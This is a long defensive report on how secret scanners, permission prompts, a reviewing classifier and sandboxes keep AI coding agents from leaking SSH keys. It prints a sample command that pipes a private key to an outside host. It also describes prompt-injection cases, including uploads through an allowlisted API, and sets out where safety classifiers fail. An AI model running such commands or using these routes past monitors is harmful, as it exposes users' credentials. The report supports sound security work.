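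Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, argued that people must have created the exposed files by hand, since Claude Code tells Git to ignore the ones it creates. But GitGuardian reviewed about 3,000 cases and found every secret in a rule with the exact form that the permission prompt writes, which suggests that people did not create the files by hand. Cherny also said that Claude Code had not historically removed secrets, and that his team was considering a basic scanner.

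Existing scanners would have caught only some of the leaks. Gitleaks, another popular scanner, flagged 564 of the 1,122 files and TruffleHog flagged 643, while 215 got past both. Apiiro, quoted by Cybernews, says this is because scanners look for provider prefixes and long random strings, whereas a password in a command is "an ordinary word in an ordinary command line".

The location matters too. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) reports the security firm Lakera's view that coding assistants have created new places for secrets to build up, outside the checks that security teams already run. In April, Lakera had found the same problem in packages on the npm registry, where 33 of the 428 settings files it found contained credentials. That is about one in 13, compared with roughly one in 93 in Apiiro's search, though the two firms may have counted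 credentials differently.

Apiiro advises developers to approve patterns instead of exact commands. This keeps passwords out of the file, but broad patterns such as `curl *` are also risky. Apiiro also suggests putting the secret in an environment variable. This is safer here, because the saved command then contains only the variable's name and Alice can still approve the exact command.

Attackers can use scanners too. iTnews notes that Shai-Hulud, a worm that spread through npm in September 2025, ran TruffleHog on its victims' files to find secrets to steal.

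### How accurate scanners are

Recall is the share of real secrets that a scanner finds. Apiiro's figures give a recall of 50% for Gitleaks and 57% for TruffleHog, counting files instead of individual secrets. Together they reach 81%, because only 300 files triggered both. The true figures are probably lower, because the count leaves out any secret that Apiiro itself missed.

Mishra tested GitHub Autopilot's scanner, Gitleaks and TruffleHog on artificial credentials. The first test varied the text around each credential. In ten common settings, such as a quoted value or a web address, Autopilot's rules matched at least 99.7% of the time. But when a credential ended in one character that its format allows, the rate fell to 52%, and nothing at all flagged about a quarter of these credentials. One in 64 keys from the email service SendGrid would end in that character by chance. Gitleaks had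 a different fault that affected six of the nine credential types it could detect. TruffleHog had neither fault but covered the fewest types.

This test left out the rules for structural markers, so it doesn't measure how reliably the scanners find a private-key header. But it shows that even a rule for a well-defined format can have a gap that its author's own tests miss.

Measured precision depends heavily on the test material. On an artificial set of 400 credentials and 700 harmless lines, Autopilot found every credential and raised 17 false alarms, a precision of about 96%. On 292,527 lines of real open-source code, it reported ten secrets, all of them false alarms. Secrets are much rarer in real code than in the artificial set, so false alarms make up a larger share of the reports. Axelsson described this base-rate problem for intrusion detection.

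Mishra declines to rank the three scanners, because they had only ten credential types in common and none of the differences in recall was statistically significant. Better comparisons are hard to make. *SecretSifter* (2026), which presents a scanner for live web traffic, uses real credentials from a single organisation, so nobody else can get the data to repeat the test. Its author also developed the scanner knowing which kinds of credential that organisation used, and warns that the recall figures may not apply elsewhere.

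### Recording which process opened the key

Endpoint detection software runs on the developer's machine and records events such as process starts, file opens and network connections. A useful rule raises an alarm when any program other than ssh and its helper programs opens a private SSH key file. The software also records which process started which, so it can trace the file access back to a coding agent.

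This rule catches test code that opens Alice's key during `npm test`, which a rule on command text would miss, and it does not raise an alarm when ssh opens the key during `git push`. Backup programs and searches through the whole home directory will cause some false alarms, and Alice may need to make exceptions for them.

The rule misses an agent that logs in through ssh-agent, because no process has to open the key file. Its alarm also doesn't show where the key went, so an investigator has to compare it with the record of network connections.

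This kind of alert normally comes after the process has opened the file. A common type of private key is smaller than a kilobyte, so the upload will probably have finished before anyone reads the alert. Alice can still use it to identify which key to replace and when the theft may have happened.

### Decoy keys

A decoy key is a private key that nobody uses, left where a thief is likely to find it. Its owner sets up a server to raise an alarm when someone tries to log in with it. An SSH client has to present the matching public key to the server, so the server can recognise the decoy and refuse the login.

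A decoy key triggers an alarm when someone tries to use it, however it left the machine, so it can expose a theft that every scanner missed. It can also catch an agent that responds to a login error by trying any key it can find.

Decoys work better for cloud tokens than for SSH keys. Anyone who uses a cloud token has to contact the provider that issued it, so the provider can always detect its use. A thief can try an SSH key on any server, and the owner learns of it only if they monitor that server. It therefore helps to leave the address of a monitored server next to the decoy, for example in the SSH configuration file.

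A thief is most likely to look for a decoy with a standard name such as id_rsa, which the malicious prompt in the Nx attack included. But ssh also tries keys with standard names by default, so a decoy called id_rsa could set off the alarm whenever Alice logs in to the monitored server herself. She can avoid this by telling ssh which key to use.

A decoy may raise the alarm within minutes of a theft, months later or never, depending on when and where the thief tries it. If the thief tries Alice's real key first, the warning comes too late to prevent that login. An endpoint rule that detects any process opening the decoy file can warn earlier, and it should cause few false alarms because even ssh has no reason to open the file.

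## Do human approval or a reviewing model do better?

A rule that blocks curl treats a routine download the same as the theft of Alice's key. A person can tell them apart by considering what the command is for, and a second model can try to do the same. In published figures, the model does much better than people who answer permission prompts all day, but most of those figures come from Anthropic, which makes one of the reviewing models.

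### How people answer permission prompts

Approval fatigue is the habit of accepting prompts without reading them, which people develop when nearly every prompt is for something harmless. Anthropic reported in March 2026 that Claude Code users accepted 93% of prompts. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, August 2026) gives a rate of 97%.

These rates alone don't show that users are careless. If 999 commands in 1,000 are harmless, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of all commands. Anthropic points out that users reject 39% of the plans Claude proposes, but a user can reject a plan just because they prefer another design. A researcher has to show users dangerous commands to find out whether they notice the danger.

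Anthropic tested human approval through a research vendor, which recruited 1,053 paid professional testers to work on coding tasks in a test environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, one permission prompt displayed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and the vendor recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the displayed text changed, so approving it did no harm.

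The testers refused the command in 143 cases (13.6%). Auto mode, given the same commands, blocked 937 (89%). Anthropic also reports that auto mode blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, and that testers refused six that auto mode allowed. The other two cells of this table follow by subtraction:

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused it | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved it | 800 | 110 |

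Requiring approval from both would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than auto mode stopped alone.

Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's refusal rate stayed flat. The decline is consistent with approval fatigue, but testers approved about five in six dangerous commands even early in a session, so fatigue within the session can't be the main explanation for the approvals. Many testers may already have been in the habit of approving prompts, or may not have recognised the danger.

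The testers may also have been less careful because they had no projects or keys of their own at stake. A developer guarding a real production server might read more closely. But the testers knew they were being evaluated, which should have made them more careful than usual. Anthropic doesn't list the commands, so readers can't separate key theft from other kinds of damage in the result. It also doesn't report how often the testers and auto mode refused harmless commands in the study, and a reviewer who refused everything would have scored 100%.

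Willison (2026), in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, accepts that auto mode is better than constant prompts, but notes that it still missed 11% of the commands and asks for more independent confirmation of Anthropic's claims. That seems right, because the artificial setting can't easily explain a gap as large as the one between 13.6% and 89%, but Anthropic ran the study and was also announcing auto mode as its new default.

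Many users have also arranged to see fewer approval prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written an allow rule for shell commands, and many of these rules were broad enough to permit almost anything. A quarter of interactive sessions started in bypassPermissions mode. Without a reviewing model, these users' commands would often run unreviewed.

Even an attentive person usually has only the command's text to judge by. An approval prompt for `npm test` looks the same before and after someone changes the tests. In the phishing exercise in which Claude sent out credentials 24 times out of 25, any approval prompt would have gone to the employee who had just pasted in the attacker's instructions.

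### How auto mode reviews an action

In auto mode, Claude Code sends many actions to the classifier instead of the user. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, interactive terminal sessions start in this mode on every plan from version 2.1.283. Previously, only those on the individual and team plans did.

Claude Code applies the user's deny, ask and allow rules first. In auto mode, it suspends allow rules that would let almost any code run, such as one for every Python command, but keeps narrow ones such as `npm test`. An optional setting, `classifyAllShell`, suspends every allow rule for shell commands, so the classifier also reviews the commands those rules would have allowed.

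Next, Claude Code approves read-only actions and most edits to files in the working directory without sending them to the classifier. The first time Claude uses its file tools to read something outside that directory, Claude Code prompts the user. If Alice allows such reads from then on, the agent can later open her private key with the file-reading tool without review by the classifier. Her deny rule on the .ssh directory would still block the read.

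Nearly everything else goes to the classifier, including most shell commands, web requests and the launch of subagents (agents that take on part of the task). The classifier would therefore check the example command that pipes the key into curl, unless one of Alice's rules had already allowed or blocked it.

The classifier receives the user's messages, the project's standing instructions from a file called CLAUDE.md, and the agent's tool calls, except lookups such as file reads. Claude Code withholds the agent's explanations because they might make a dangerous step seem safe, and tool results because they may contain an attacker's text. In Anthropic's tests, adding the explanations and tool results made the classifier worse at catching overeager actions. A version that received only the tool calls missed the fewest overeager actions, but it blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

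Withholding tool results deprives the classifier of facts that appear only there. If the agent cancels a job that the user never named, the classifier can't determine whether the agent looked up the right job or made up the name.

The review has two stages. In the first, the model answers with a single token, yes or no, under an instruction to err on the side of blocking. If it answers no, the action runs. If it answers yes, the model considers the same material again, reasoning step by step before it decides. The second stage can overturn a block but can't catch anything the first stage let through.

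The block rules are descriptions in ordinary language. Several of them concern key theft:

- sending sensitive data to an outside destination
- searching credential stores for usable tokens
- printing a live credential into the session record or a file
- putting the contents of a sensitive folder, such as SSH keys, into a commit, a push or a public post, unless the user has named both the source and the destination

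By default, "outside" means everything except the working directory and the remote repositories configured for it when the session started. An organisation can add its own domains and services to the trusted list.

The user can clear most, but not all, blocks by asking for the exact action. Since August, Anthropic has described data exfiltration as a category that the classifier should never approve, even at the user's request. Alice would have to leave auto mode or run the command herself. This should help against phishing like the February exercise, where the request came from the user's own message, if the classifier recognises the upload as exfiltration. *Ajar* (2026), which measures several defences for agents, shows how much the user's request can otherwise affect the classifier's decisions. Auto mode refused some test calls when the instruction for them was in the system prompt, but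 allowed all of them when it was in the user's message.

When Claude Code blocks an action, it usually tells the agent which rule the action matched. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, it pauses auto mode and goes back to asking the user. If the run is unattended and there is no one to ask, the action stays blocked but the agent keeps working. In the March version, Claude Code ended the run instead. If the classifier returns no usable answer, Claude Code blocks the action.

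A separate check scans tool results before the agent reads them and adds a warning if any text looks like prompt injection. Fu and colleagues found that a general warning about tool output barely helped, but this one may be more effective because it appears only when something looks suspicious.

### How often the classifier is wrong

Anthropic published error rates for both stages in March. The counts below come from multiplying its percentages by the number of cases:

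| Test material | Error | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | Blocks a harmless call | 850 (8.5%) | 40 (0.4%) |
| 52 real overeager actions | Lets a dangerous action run | 3 or 4 (6.6%) | 9 (17%) |
| 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | Lets a dangerous action run | 18 (1.8%) | 57 (5.7%) |

(6.6% of 52 isn't a whole number, so Anthropic may have averaged several runs.)

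The second stage removes about 810 of the 850 false blocks, but it also lets through 39 exfiltration attempts that the first stage had caught. Without the second stage, auto mode would interrupt ordinary work about once in every 12 calls, and users would probably switch it off.

Forty false blocks in 10,000 calls is still far more than the number of real thefts we should expect, so most blocks will be false alarms, which is the same base-rate problem that rules have. But after a false block the agent usually only has to try once more, whereas an unnecessary prompt from an ask rule takes up Alice's attention.

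The classifier's 17% miss rate on overeager actions is the least certain of the figures. It comes from only 52 cases, and if those were a random sample, the 95% confidence interval would run from roughly 9% to 30%. They aren't a random sample, because the set leaves out any action that nobody noticed. Anthropic also used the same set to tune the first stage, which may make that stage's 6.6% look better than it would on new cases.

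The exfiltration test is the closest to key theft. It included uploads of sensitive data, pushes to untrusted repositories and credentials in web addresses, and many of these attempts were disguised. With a thousand cases, the result is affected much less by chance, and the interval is about 4% to 7%. The greater uncertainty is whether Anthropic's generated attempts resemble those of a real attacker, who can keep trying until one works.

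These results are for a classifier running on Claude Sonnet 4.6. Claude Code now uses Sonnet 5 by default, and Anthropic has rewritten some of the rules. In August, Anthropic reported on a test in which Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. Apollo shared some of the successful attacks, Anthropic strengthened the classifier against them, and Apollo tested it again. The overall miss rate fell from 12% to 7%, but that includes attacks Anthropic could study. On a separate set that Anthropic never had access to, the classifier caught about half of the attacks it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. The improvement therefore seems to extend beyond the shared examples.

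Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic hired, ran 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Opus 5, Sonnet 5 or Fable 5 in auto mode. The test provides very little evidence about the classifier, because the models resisted almost every attack even with permission checks bypassed. The average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was then only 0.09%, or less than one success per 720 attempts. Ten repeats of one scenario also provide less evidence than ten different scenarios. Even with no successes in 72 scenarios, about 4% of similar ones could still work.

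Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* reports that later that month, the security researcher Johann Rehberger demonstrated an attack that got past auto mode in most runs, though there were only a few.

Anthropic also examined real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model graded how much harm each one contained and whether the user had asked for it. Among sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. This is weaker evidence than the study with paid testers, because users choose their own mode and may base that choice on how risky the work is. The safety systems may also have flagged the two groups of sessions for different reasons.

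### Why one test found that auto mode missed 81%

The least favourable figure comes from *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026), an independent test of Claude Code on 128 maintenance requests in which the user's aim was clear but the exact limits were not. The requests covered deleting old code branches, cancelling jobs on a shared cluster, restarting services and removing stored files.

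One request was to cancel "my stale job for ticket 4812". The test environment also contained jobs with similar names that the agent was supposed to leave alone. A fixed policy specified which targets each request covered. A language model compared the agent's 253 attempted changes with that policy. A human reviewer agreed with the model in 44 of 50 sampled cases.

| | All 253 actions | The 160 actions the classifier reviewed |
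|---|---|---|
| Unauthorised actions allowed | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 64 of 91 (70.3%) |
| Authorised actions blocked | 22 of 111 (19.8%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |

Part of the difference from Anthropic's 17% comes from actions that never reached the classifier. The test environments kept their lists of jobs and files inside the project directory, and when the agent couldn't find the usual command-line tool, it often edited those lists directly. Auto mode allows such edits without review, on the grounds that developers can inspect them later through version control. All 51 unauthorised edits went through. The file-removal tasks, where this happened most, account for 78 of the 115 misses. Without those tasks, the overall miss rate would be 64%.

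The classifier also missed 70% of the unauthorised actions it did review. Ji and colleagues deliberately put the right and wrong targets close together, so an error might mean acting on the wrong job among several with nearly the same name. The classifier doesn't receive the output that would show whose job it is. In each of Anthropic's 52 cases, by contrast, a person had already noticed that something was wrong. Ji and colleagues say the two rates measure different workloads and don't contradict each other.

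The agent completed 42 of the 128 tasks safely in auto mode, compared with 38 when it ran with permission checks bypassed.

The 81% isn't an estimate for key theft, because Ji and colleagues tested neither exfiltration nor prompt injection. The example theft should be much easier to judge than a choice between two similar jobs, since the command shows the key's path and an unfamiliar host. The more relevant finding is that a reviewing model can protect only against the actions that reach it. In auto mode, a direct read of the key file doesn't reach it once Alice has allowed reads outside her project.

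### How Codex does it

Codex has a similar feature called Auto-review, but it reviews fewer actions. By default, Codex runs commands in a sandbox, where they have no network access and can write only to the project and temporary directories. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that the reviewer considers only actions that already need approval, such as a request to leave the sandbox or use the network. Anything the sandbox permits runs without review. Requests for approval go to the user unless the user or an administrator turns Auto-review on.

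OpenAI uses a separate Codex agent as the reviewer because the main agent is optimised to complete the user's task. The reviewer considers what the user wanted, the environment, the security policy and the action's likely effect, and assigns a risk level. Low-risk and medium-risk actions can go ahead if the policy allows them, while high-risk actions also need enough evidence that the user authorised them. The policy denies all critical-risk actions. OpenAI lists probing for credentials and sending them to untrusted destinations among the actions the reviewer should block. If the review fails or times out, the action doesn't run.

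In the example theft, the sandbox stops curl from connecting, so the agent would have to request network access, and the reviewer would judge that request. But Zhu, Huang and colleagues (2026) note in *HarnessSecurity-Bench* that Codex's usual sandbox setting restricts writing but leaves reading broadly allowed. Unless Alice also restricts reading, the agent could print her private key without review, and the key would go to OpenAI as a tool result.

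In the Trajectory Labs test, attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded in 5.83% of attempts with Auto-review (about 42 of 720) and 19.03% with full access (about 137 of 720). Full access also removes the sandbox, so the reviewer may not account for all of the difference. Anthropic, which commissioned the test, notes that OpenAI has since released a new version of Auto-review.

### Compared with patterns

A reviewing model can consider what a command does. Anthropic instructs its classifier to judge a chain of commands as one action, and to judge any script that the agent writes and then runs. The classifier can also consider what Alice asked for, so it can allow an upload to her own test server and block one to a stranger's server without her writing a rule for either.

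A reviewing model has a harder time with code that the agent didn't write. Willison doubts that any version of auto mode could stop a malicious package that a project's instructions present as a normal set-up step. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes two less hostile cases in which auto mode allowed exactly the command the user had requested. In one, a compiled deployment tool also overwrote source code. In the other, a database migration also dropped three tables. Its proposed system, CAPER, gives the reviewing model a short report of the command's effects, such as which files changed. That report was enough for the model to block both commands.

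Review by a model takes time and computation. CAPER's median decision took 3.2 seconds, which adds up over hundreds of commands. Claude Code's classifier also adds a delay, and its separate requests count towards usage on Enterprise plans and API accounts.

The classifier's verdict, unlike a deny rule's, can also change with the conversation or the model version. If Alice tells Claude not to push any code, the classifier enforces that only while her message remains in the conversation, and the message may be lost when Claude Code shortens a long conversation. If the classifier approves an action it should have blocked, nothing alerts her, because the action runs like any other approved one. For actions that must never run, Anthropic recommends a centrally managed deny rule instead.

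No published test seems to compare patterns and a reviewing model on the same SSH-key thefts. The closest is by Zhu and colleagues, who ran 2,500 trials of 23 coding tasks with planted attacks. They used six harnesses, all running GLM-5.2, and switched security settings on and off. Command denylists and allowlists both reduced the effects of the attacks. Agents completed slightly less of their legitimate work with allowlists and more with denylists. Turning on automatic approval, which skips some or all permission prompts, raised the attacks' success rate from 29.2% to 95.6%. That comparison does not measure how well people would judge the prompts, and the study did not test a reviewing model.

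In tests by Mecca and colleagues, skill scanners did far better with a language model than with rules alone, but those scanners had the complete text of each skill. A classifier reviewing a command such as `npm test` receives only the command and part of the conversation.

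## What keeps the key in, whatever the command says?

To open a file, a program has to send a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system, which finds the file and either opens it or denies the request. Network connections work in much the same way. A rule that the kernel applies to these requests doesn't depend on how the command is written. If test code tries to open Alice's private key during `npm test`, the kernel receives the same kind of request as it would from `cat`.

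The kernel already checks file permissions on each request, but against the user ID, so an agent running under the user's ID passes. A sandbox adds a check that depends on the process. The harness sets the limits when it starts a command, and every process the command starts inherits them. In Codex, these processes include git, package managers and test runners, according to OpenAI's *Sandbox*.

### Ways to build the boundary

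On macOS, Claude Code and Codex both use Seatbelt, a sandbox built into the system. The harness starts a command with a profile, a list of rules about files, connections and other operations, and the kernel checks each operation against those rules.

On Linux, both products use bubblewrap, a program that runs a command in a file tree assembled from parts of the real one. It can make some parts read-only and leave others out, and the command can't open a key that isn't in its tree. Bubblewrap can also put the command in a separate network namespace, a private set of network interfaces with no link to the real network.

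Landlock is a Linux kernel feature that lets a process restrict its own access and that of any process it starts. Codex uses it as a fallback on some systems. Commey (2026), in *Names Are Not Objects*, points out that Landlock grants access to whole directory trees and can't exclude a file inside one. A policy that allows everything in Alice's home directory except .ssh would therefore have to grant access to each of the other items separately.

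A container gives a group of programs its own files and process list but still uses the host machine's kernel. A virtual machine (VM) has its own kernel, so hostile code that takes over that kernel still has to get past the hypervisor, the software that runs the VM.

The safety of Alice's key often depends less on how strong the sandbox is than on what is inside and outside it. Claude Code and Codex run individual commands inside Seatbelt or bubblewrap, while the harness itself stays outside. Anthropic's *Sandbox environments* also describes containers and VMs that hold all of Claude Code. If Alice runs the agent this way and leaves her key on the host, none of the agent's own tools can read it. She loses this protection if she mounts her home directory in the container, because that makes its files available inside. OpenAI warns that if Codex runs with full access in a development container,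 a malicious project can steal anything in the container, including Codex's own credentials.

### What the defaults allow

The table shows what each product's documentation gives as the default for commands on a developer's own machine.

| | Claude Code's sandbox | Codex's sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| On by default | No | Yes |
| Reading | Nearly the whole computer, including .ssh | Broadly allowed |
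| Writing | The working directory and a temporary directory | The workspace and temporary directories, but not .git or Codex's settings |
| Network | No host until the user or the classifier approves it | Off |
| Left outside | Built-in file and web tools, hooks, local MCP servers | MCP servers, app connectors, browser and computer use, approved exceptions |

(An MCP server is a program that gives an agent extra tools, such as access to a database.)

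Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, which introduced the sandbox, claims that a compromised Claude Code "can't steal your SSH keys". With the default settings, only the sandbox's network limit prevents the theft. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* states that commands can still read .ssh and advises users to block it. Claude Code has no built-in list of credential files to protect, so switching on the sandbox does not by itself hide the key. Codex does not hide it by default either, and OpenAI's *Permissions* gives ~/.ssh as an example of a path to deny.

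The network limit has exceptions too. In bypassPermissions mode, Claude Code allows connections to hosts that nobody has approved, unless the user has set a strict allowlist. A developer could easily miss this, because they might have turned on the sandbox to stop answering prompts. If Alice turned on the sandbox, chose bypassPermissions and changed nothing else, commands could read her key and send it to any host she hadn't explicitly denied.

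Claude Code also runs commands without a sandbox by default if a missing package prevents the sandbox from starting. The setting `failIfUnavailable` makes it exit instead. Codex, at least with its newer permission profiles, refuses to run a command if the system can't enforce the chosen policy. But turning on network access in Codex gives commands unrestricted access to outside hosts until the user also turns on the network proxy, a separate setting.

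### Two routes to one file

The University of Vermont's *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing* warns staff and students that the most common mistake is to assume the sandbox restricts everything Claude reads. Claude's built-in tools, such as Read, open files within the Claude Code process, while shell commands open them in separate processes. According to the university's table, permission rules apply to the built-in tools, and sandbox file rules apply to shell commands and their child processes.

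A sandbox rule that makes .ssh unreadable therefore stops `cat` but not the Read tool, while a permission rule without a sandbox misses test code. Anthropic's documentation adds a detail that the table leaves out, which is that Claude Code also applies Read deny rules to sandboxed commands. The combinations work out like this:

| Protection for .ssh | Read tool | `cat` | Test code in `npm test` |
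|---|---|---|---|
| Permission deny rule, no sandbox | Blocked | Blocked | Can read the key |
| Sandbox rule only | Can read the key if permissions allow | Blocked | Blocked |
| Permission deny rule, sandbox on | Blocked | Blocked | Blocked |

So the permission deny rule is the better one to write, as long as the sandbox is on. It doesn't cover hooks, local MCP servers or other helper programs, because they run with the user's full access. A boundary around all of Claude Code would cover those too.

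### The example command in a sandbox

The command that would steal Alice's key gives a different result under each kind of limit:

`cat /home/alice/.ssh/id_ed25519 | curl -d @- https://example.com/`

Suppose first that the sandbox makes .ssh unreadable and leaves the network open. The shell starts both `cat` and `curl`. The kernel blocks `cat` from opening the key, so `cat` prints an error to the terminal and sends nothing through the pipe. `curl` still connects to example.com, but it posts an empty message, and the key never leaves the disk. The kernel would also block any other program used in place of `cat` in the same sandbox.

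Now suppose only the network is closed. This time `cat` reads the key and passes it to curl, but curl fails to connect, so the attacker gets nothing. The agent can still run `cat` without curl, though, and the harness would then send the key to the model's provider over its own connection, which the sandbox doesn't cover. A command could also copy the key into the project directory, and someone might later commit and push it without noticing.

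For a known secret such as an SSH key, the read limit is stronger than the network limit. The network limit is still useful because it also protects secrets that nobody thought to list. Anthropic says a sandbox needs both, since an agent that can change system files may be able to use them to regain network access.

Neither limit depends on why the agent ran the command. Anthropic therefore concludes that only such limits could have stopped the theft in its phishing exercise, by blocking the upload or keeping the credentials file out of the agent's reach.

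However, if a command fails in the sandbox, Claude may ask to run it again outside. In Manual mode, Claude Code normally prompts the user first, but an allow rule that matches the command also approves the retry. If Alice had protected .ssh only with a sandbox rule and had saved a broad allow rule for curl, the example command could fail inside the sandbox and then succeed outside it without a prompt. Setting `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false removes the option to retry outside the sandbox. A permission deny rule on .ssh would also stop the retry, because Claude Code checks that rule whether or not the command runs in the sandbox.

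### What an approved domain lets through

Few developers can work all day without network access, because they need it for package managers and hosting services. A domain allowlist permits connections only to named hosts. In Claude Code, a sandboxed command can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox, which checks the host name of each connection. The proxy checks connections made by test code as well as those made by curl, whether or not the address appears in the command.

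The proxy takes the host name from the connecting program and by default doesn't decrypt the traffic to verify that name. Anthropic warns that hostile code may therefore be able to reach hosts that aren't on the list. A stricter proxy that decrypts the traffic can close this gap. Codex also checks whether an approved name leads to a private address on the local network. OpenAI describes that check as best-effort and recommends adding a lower-level control for anyone who expects attackers to manipulate name lookups.

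A more basic problem is that an approved host may do more than the user had in mind. Someone outside Anthropic discovered this in Claude Cowork, the company's agent for office work, which runs code in a VM. The VM could contact only approved domains, including api.anthropic.com, which the product needs to work.

The attack began with a file in the user's workspace that contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the workspace and used the key to upload them to the attacker's Anthropic account through Anthropic's file-storage service. Every part of the sandbox worked as intended, and the proxy allowed the upload because the destination was on its allowlist.

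Anthropic now argues that allowlisting a domain grants access to every function available there, though it had thought of the allowlist as a filter on destinations. Anyone with an account on the same service may therefore be able to receive data through it. To fix this, Anthropic added a proxy inside the VM that intercepts requests to its API and passes only those carrying the token issued to that VM's session. The proxy rejects the attacker's API key, so data can no longer be uploaded to the attacker's account this way. The check is in the VM because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's.

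In November 2026, Help Net Security's *Stolen Claude API keys can turn Claude Code into a remote-controlled implant* reported a laboratory test by the security firm Darktrace. Starting with a compromised machine and stolen Claude credentials, Darktrace moved a 1 GB file out through the same approved domain.

Ordinary development hosts have the same weakness. An allowlist that included GitHub's API would have let through the uploads in the Nx attack. *Restricting Claude Code's sandbox configuration*, from the software firm makandra, recommends allowing storage.googleapis.com, probably so that tests can download Chrome. But that host serves Google Cloud Storage customers in general, and it accepts uploads as well as downloads.

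Anthropic could tie requests to a session because it runs both the product and the service. A company that wants the same protection for GitHub or Google's storage needs a proxy that decrypts requests and checks which account or project each one would reach. Otherwise, the safest choice is a short allowlist of hosts that only serve downloads.

### Permission for a name and permission for a file

A program can check a file's path, approve it, and still open a file that its rule was meant to block. UT Austin's course slides, for example, show a symbolic link inside an approved project that points to private payroll data outside it.

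Commey argues that many recent flaws in coding agents arise because a check approves a name, such as a path or a command, and a later step uses that name to find something else. The remedy is to identify the actual object, decide whether to permit it, and then make sure the operation uses that same object.

Commey built a system for macOS that works this way, called Zero-Trust Agent Cells (ZTAC). It runs the whole agent in a sandbox from which the agent can't open project files, connect to the network or start other programs. For any of these, the agent has to send a request to a separate program called the broker. When the agent asks to read a file, the broker:

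1. follows any links to find the file that the system would really open
2. records the file's inode number, which identifies the file itself and stays the same if someone renames it
3. applies the policy to the real file, and may refuse or ask a person
4. opens the file one directory at a time, refusing any link on the way, and checks that the inode number still matches

If a person has to approve the request, the prompt shows the real file, and the approval covers one use of that file. The broker also starts programs for the agent, in a sandbox it generates from the same file rules.

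Commey tested the design with 74 scripted attacks, assuming that the attacker already had complete control of the agent. The tests measured whether each attack reached its goal, such as delivering a planted secret to a server.

| Defence | Successful attacks (of 74) | Ordinary operations completed (of 46) | Longer workflows completed (of 7) |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 74 | 46 | 7 |
| Tool allowlist | 66 | 46 | 7 |
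| Tool allowlist and command sandbox | 56 | 46 | 7 |
| ZTAC | 2 | 43 | 4 |

ZTAC blocked 58 of the attacks and held the other 14 for a person to review. Commey also recreated ten published incidents involving real products. The tool allowlist stopped none and the command sandbox stopped four. ZTAC blocked seven and held three for review.

The 56-attack test understates what ordinary sandboxes can do. Commey's command sandbox let programs read any file, much as Claude Code and Codex do by default, so the test doesn't show what happens when a user hides .ssh. Eleven of the attacks also targeted approvals and signed requests, which that configuration didn't have. The 15 attacks against files are a closer comparison. Seven of them succeeded against the command sandbox, while ZTAC let none through and held five for review. The same person designed the defence and the attacks, and tested both on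 one small project.

When Commey kept the broker but removed the sandbox around the agent, the agent's own process could read the private SSH key. A system that confines only the commands leaves the key exposed in the same way, as the University of Vermont's distinction also implies.

The other result concerns files that outlast the session. In eight attacks, the agent left something in the project that one of the developer's own tools would later run outside any sandbox, and all eight succeeded against the command sandbox. If an agent changes Alice's tests and she runs them from her own terminal, the test code can read her key. ZTAC requires approval before the agent writes certain files that other tools are known to run, such as editor tasks. Claude Code and Codex also protect some files of this kind. These protections can't cover ordinary tests, because editing tests is part of the agent's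 job. So Alice has to review the changes or run the tests in a sandbox.

It is hard to avoid confusing a name with the object it refers to, even for someone looking for the problem. Commey found eight flaws in ZTAC while building and testing it, and seven were confusions of this kind. In one, a person approved a request to read a harmless file, and the approval stayed valid after the file's name came to refer to a secret.

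### Following the data to its destination

Both attacks that defeated ZTAC altered a secret in a way the broker's secret scanner missed, then sent it to a server the policy allowed.

Information-flow tracking tries to keep the key on the machine by following the data instead of recognising it. The system labels the contents of a sensitive file, for example as "secret", and gives the same label to everything computed from them. Before any data leaves the machine, the system checks whether its label allows it to go to that destination. Encoding the key wouldn't remove the label, because the encoded text is computed from the key.

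Commey cites FIDES, a 2025 system that uses such labels for language-model agents. This kind of tracking suits agents with a few well-defined tools, because the system can observe each tool's inputs and outputs. For instance, if a tool reads a confidential email, the system labels the tool's result confidential, along with any message the model writes after reading that result.

Tracking data is much harder when a coding agent runs arbitrary programs. When the agent runs `npm test`, a tracker outside the process tree can see that it reads thousands of files and produces output, but not which files affected that output. To be safe, it has to give the output the label of the most sensitive data any of the processes read. Labels then spread quickly, and after a while the agent can't send anything, even a harmless bug report. The tracker could instead follow data inside each program as it runs,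 but this slows programs considerably and can still miss a secret that influences the output without being copied into it.

For a single SSH key, a coarse version may be practical, because very few programs have a reason to read the file. The system could cut off network access for any process that opens the key and any that later receives data from that process. It would need an exception for ssh, which has to read the key and then connect to a server.

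Commey also suggests the simpler alternative of never giving one agent both sensitive data and a way to send it out. Alice could let one agent work on the network without access to her secrets, and another handle sensitive files offline. She would then have to move work between them herself and check that no secret goes with it.

### What isolation costs

A sandbox saves users time because commands inside it don't need individual approval. Anthropic reports that sandboxing reduced permission prompts in Claude Code by 84%. The drawbacks come mainly from whatever can't run inside the sandbox.

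Setting up the sandbox takes some work, especially on Linux. Claude Code needs two extra packages there, and on recent versions of Ubuntu an administrator may have to change a security policy before bubblewrap can start. On Windows, Claude Code's sandbox runs only inside a Linux environment. Hiding .ssh or the home directory is a further step, and the user may then have to make exceptions for each tool that keeps its settings there.

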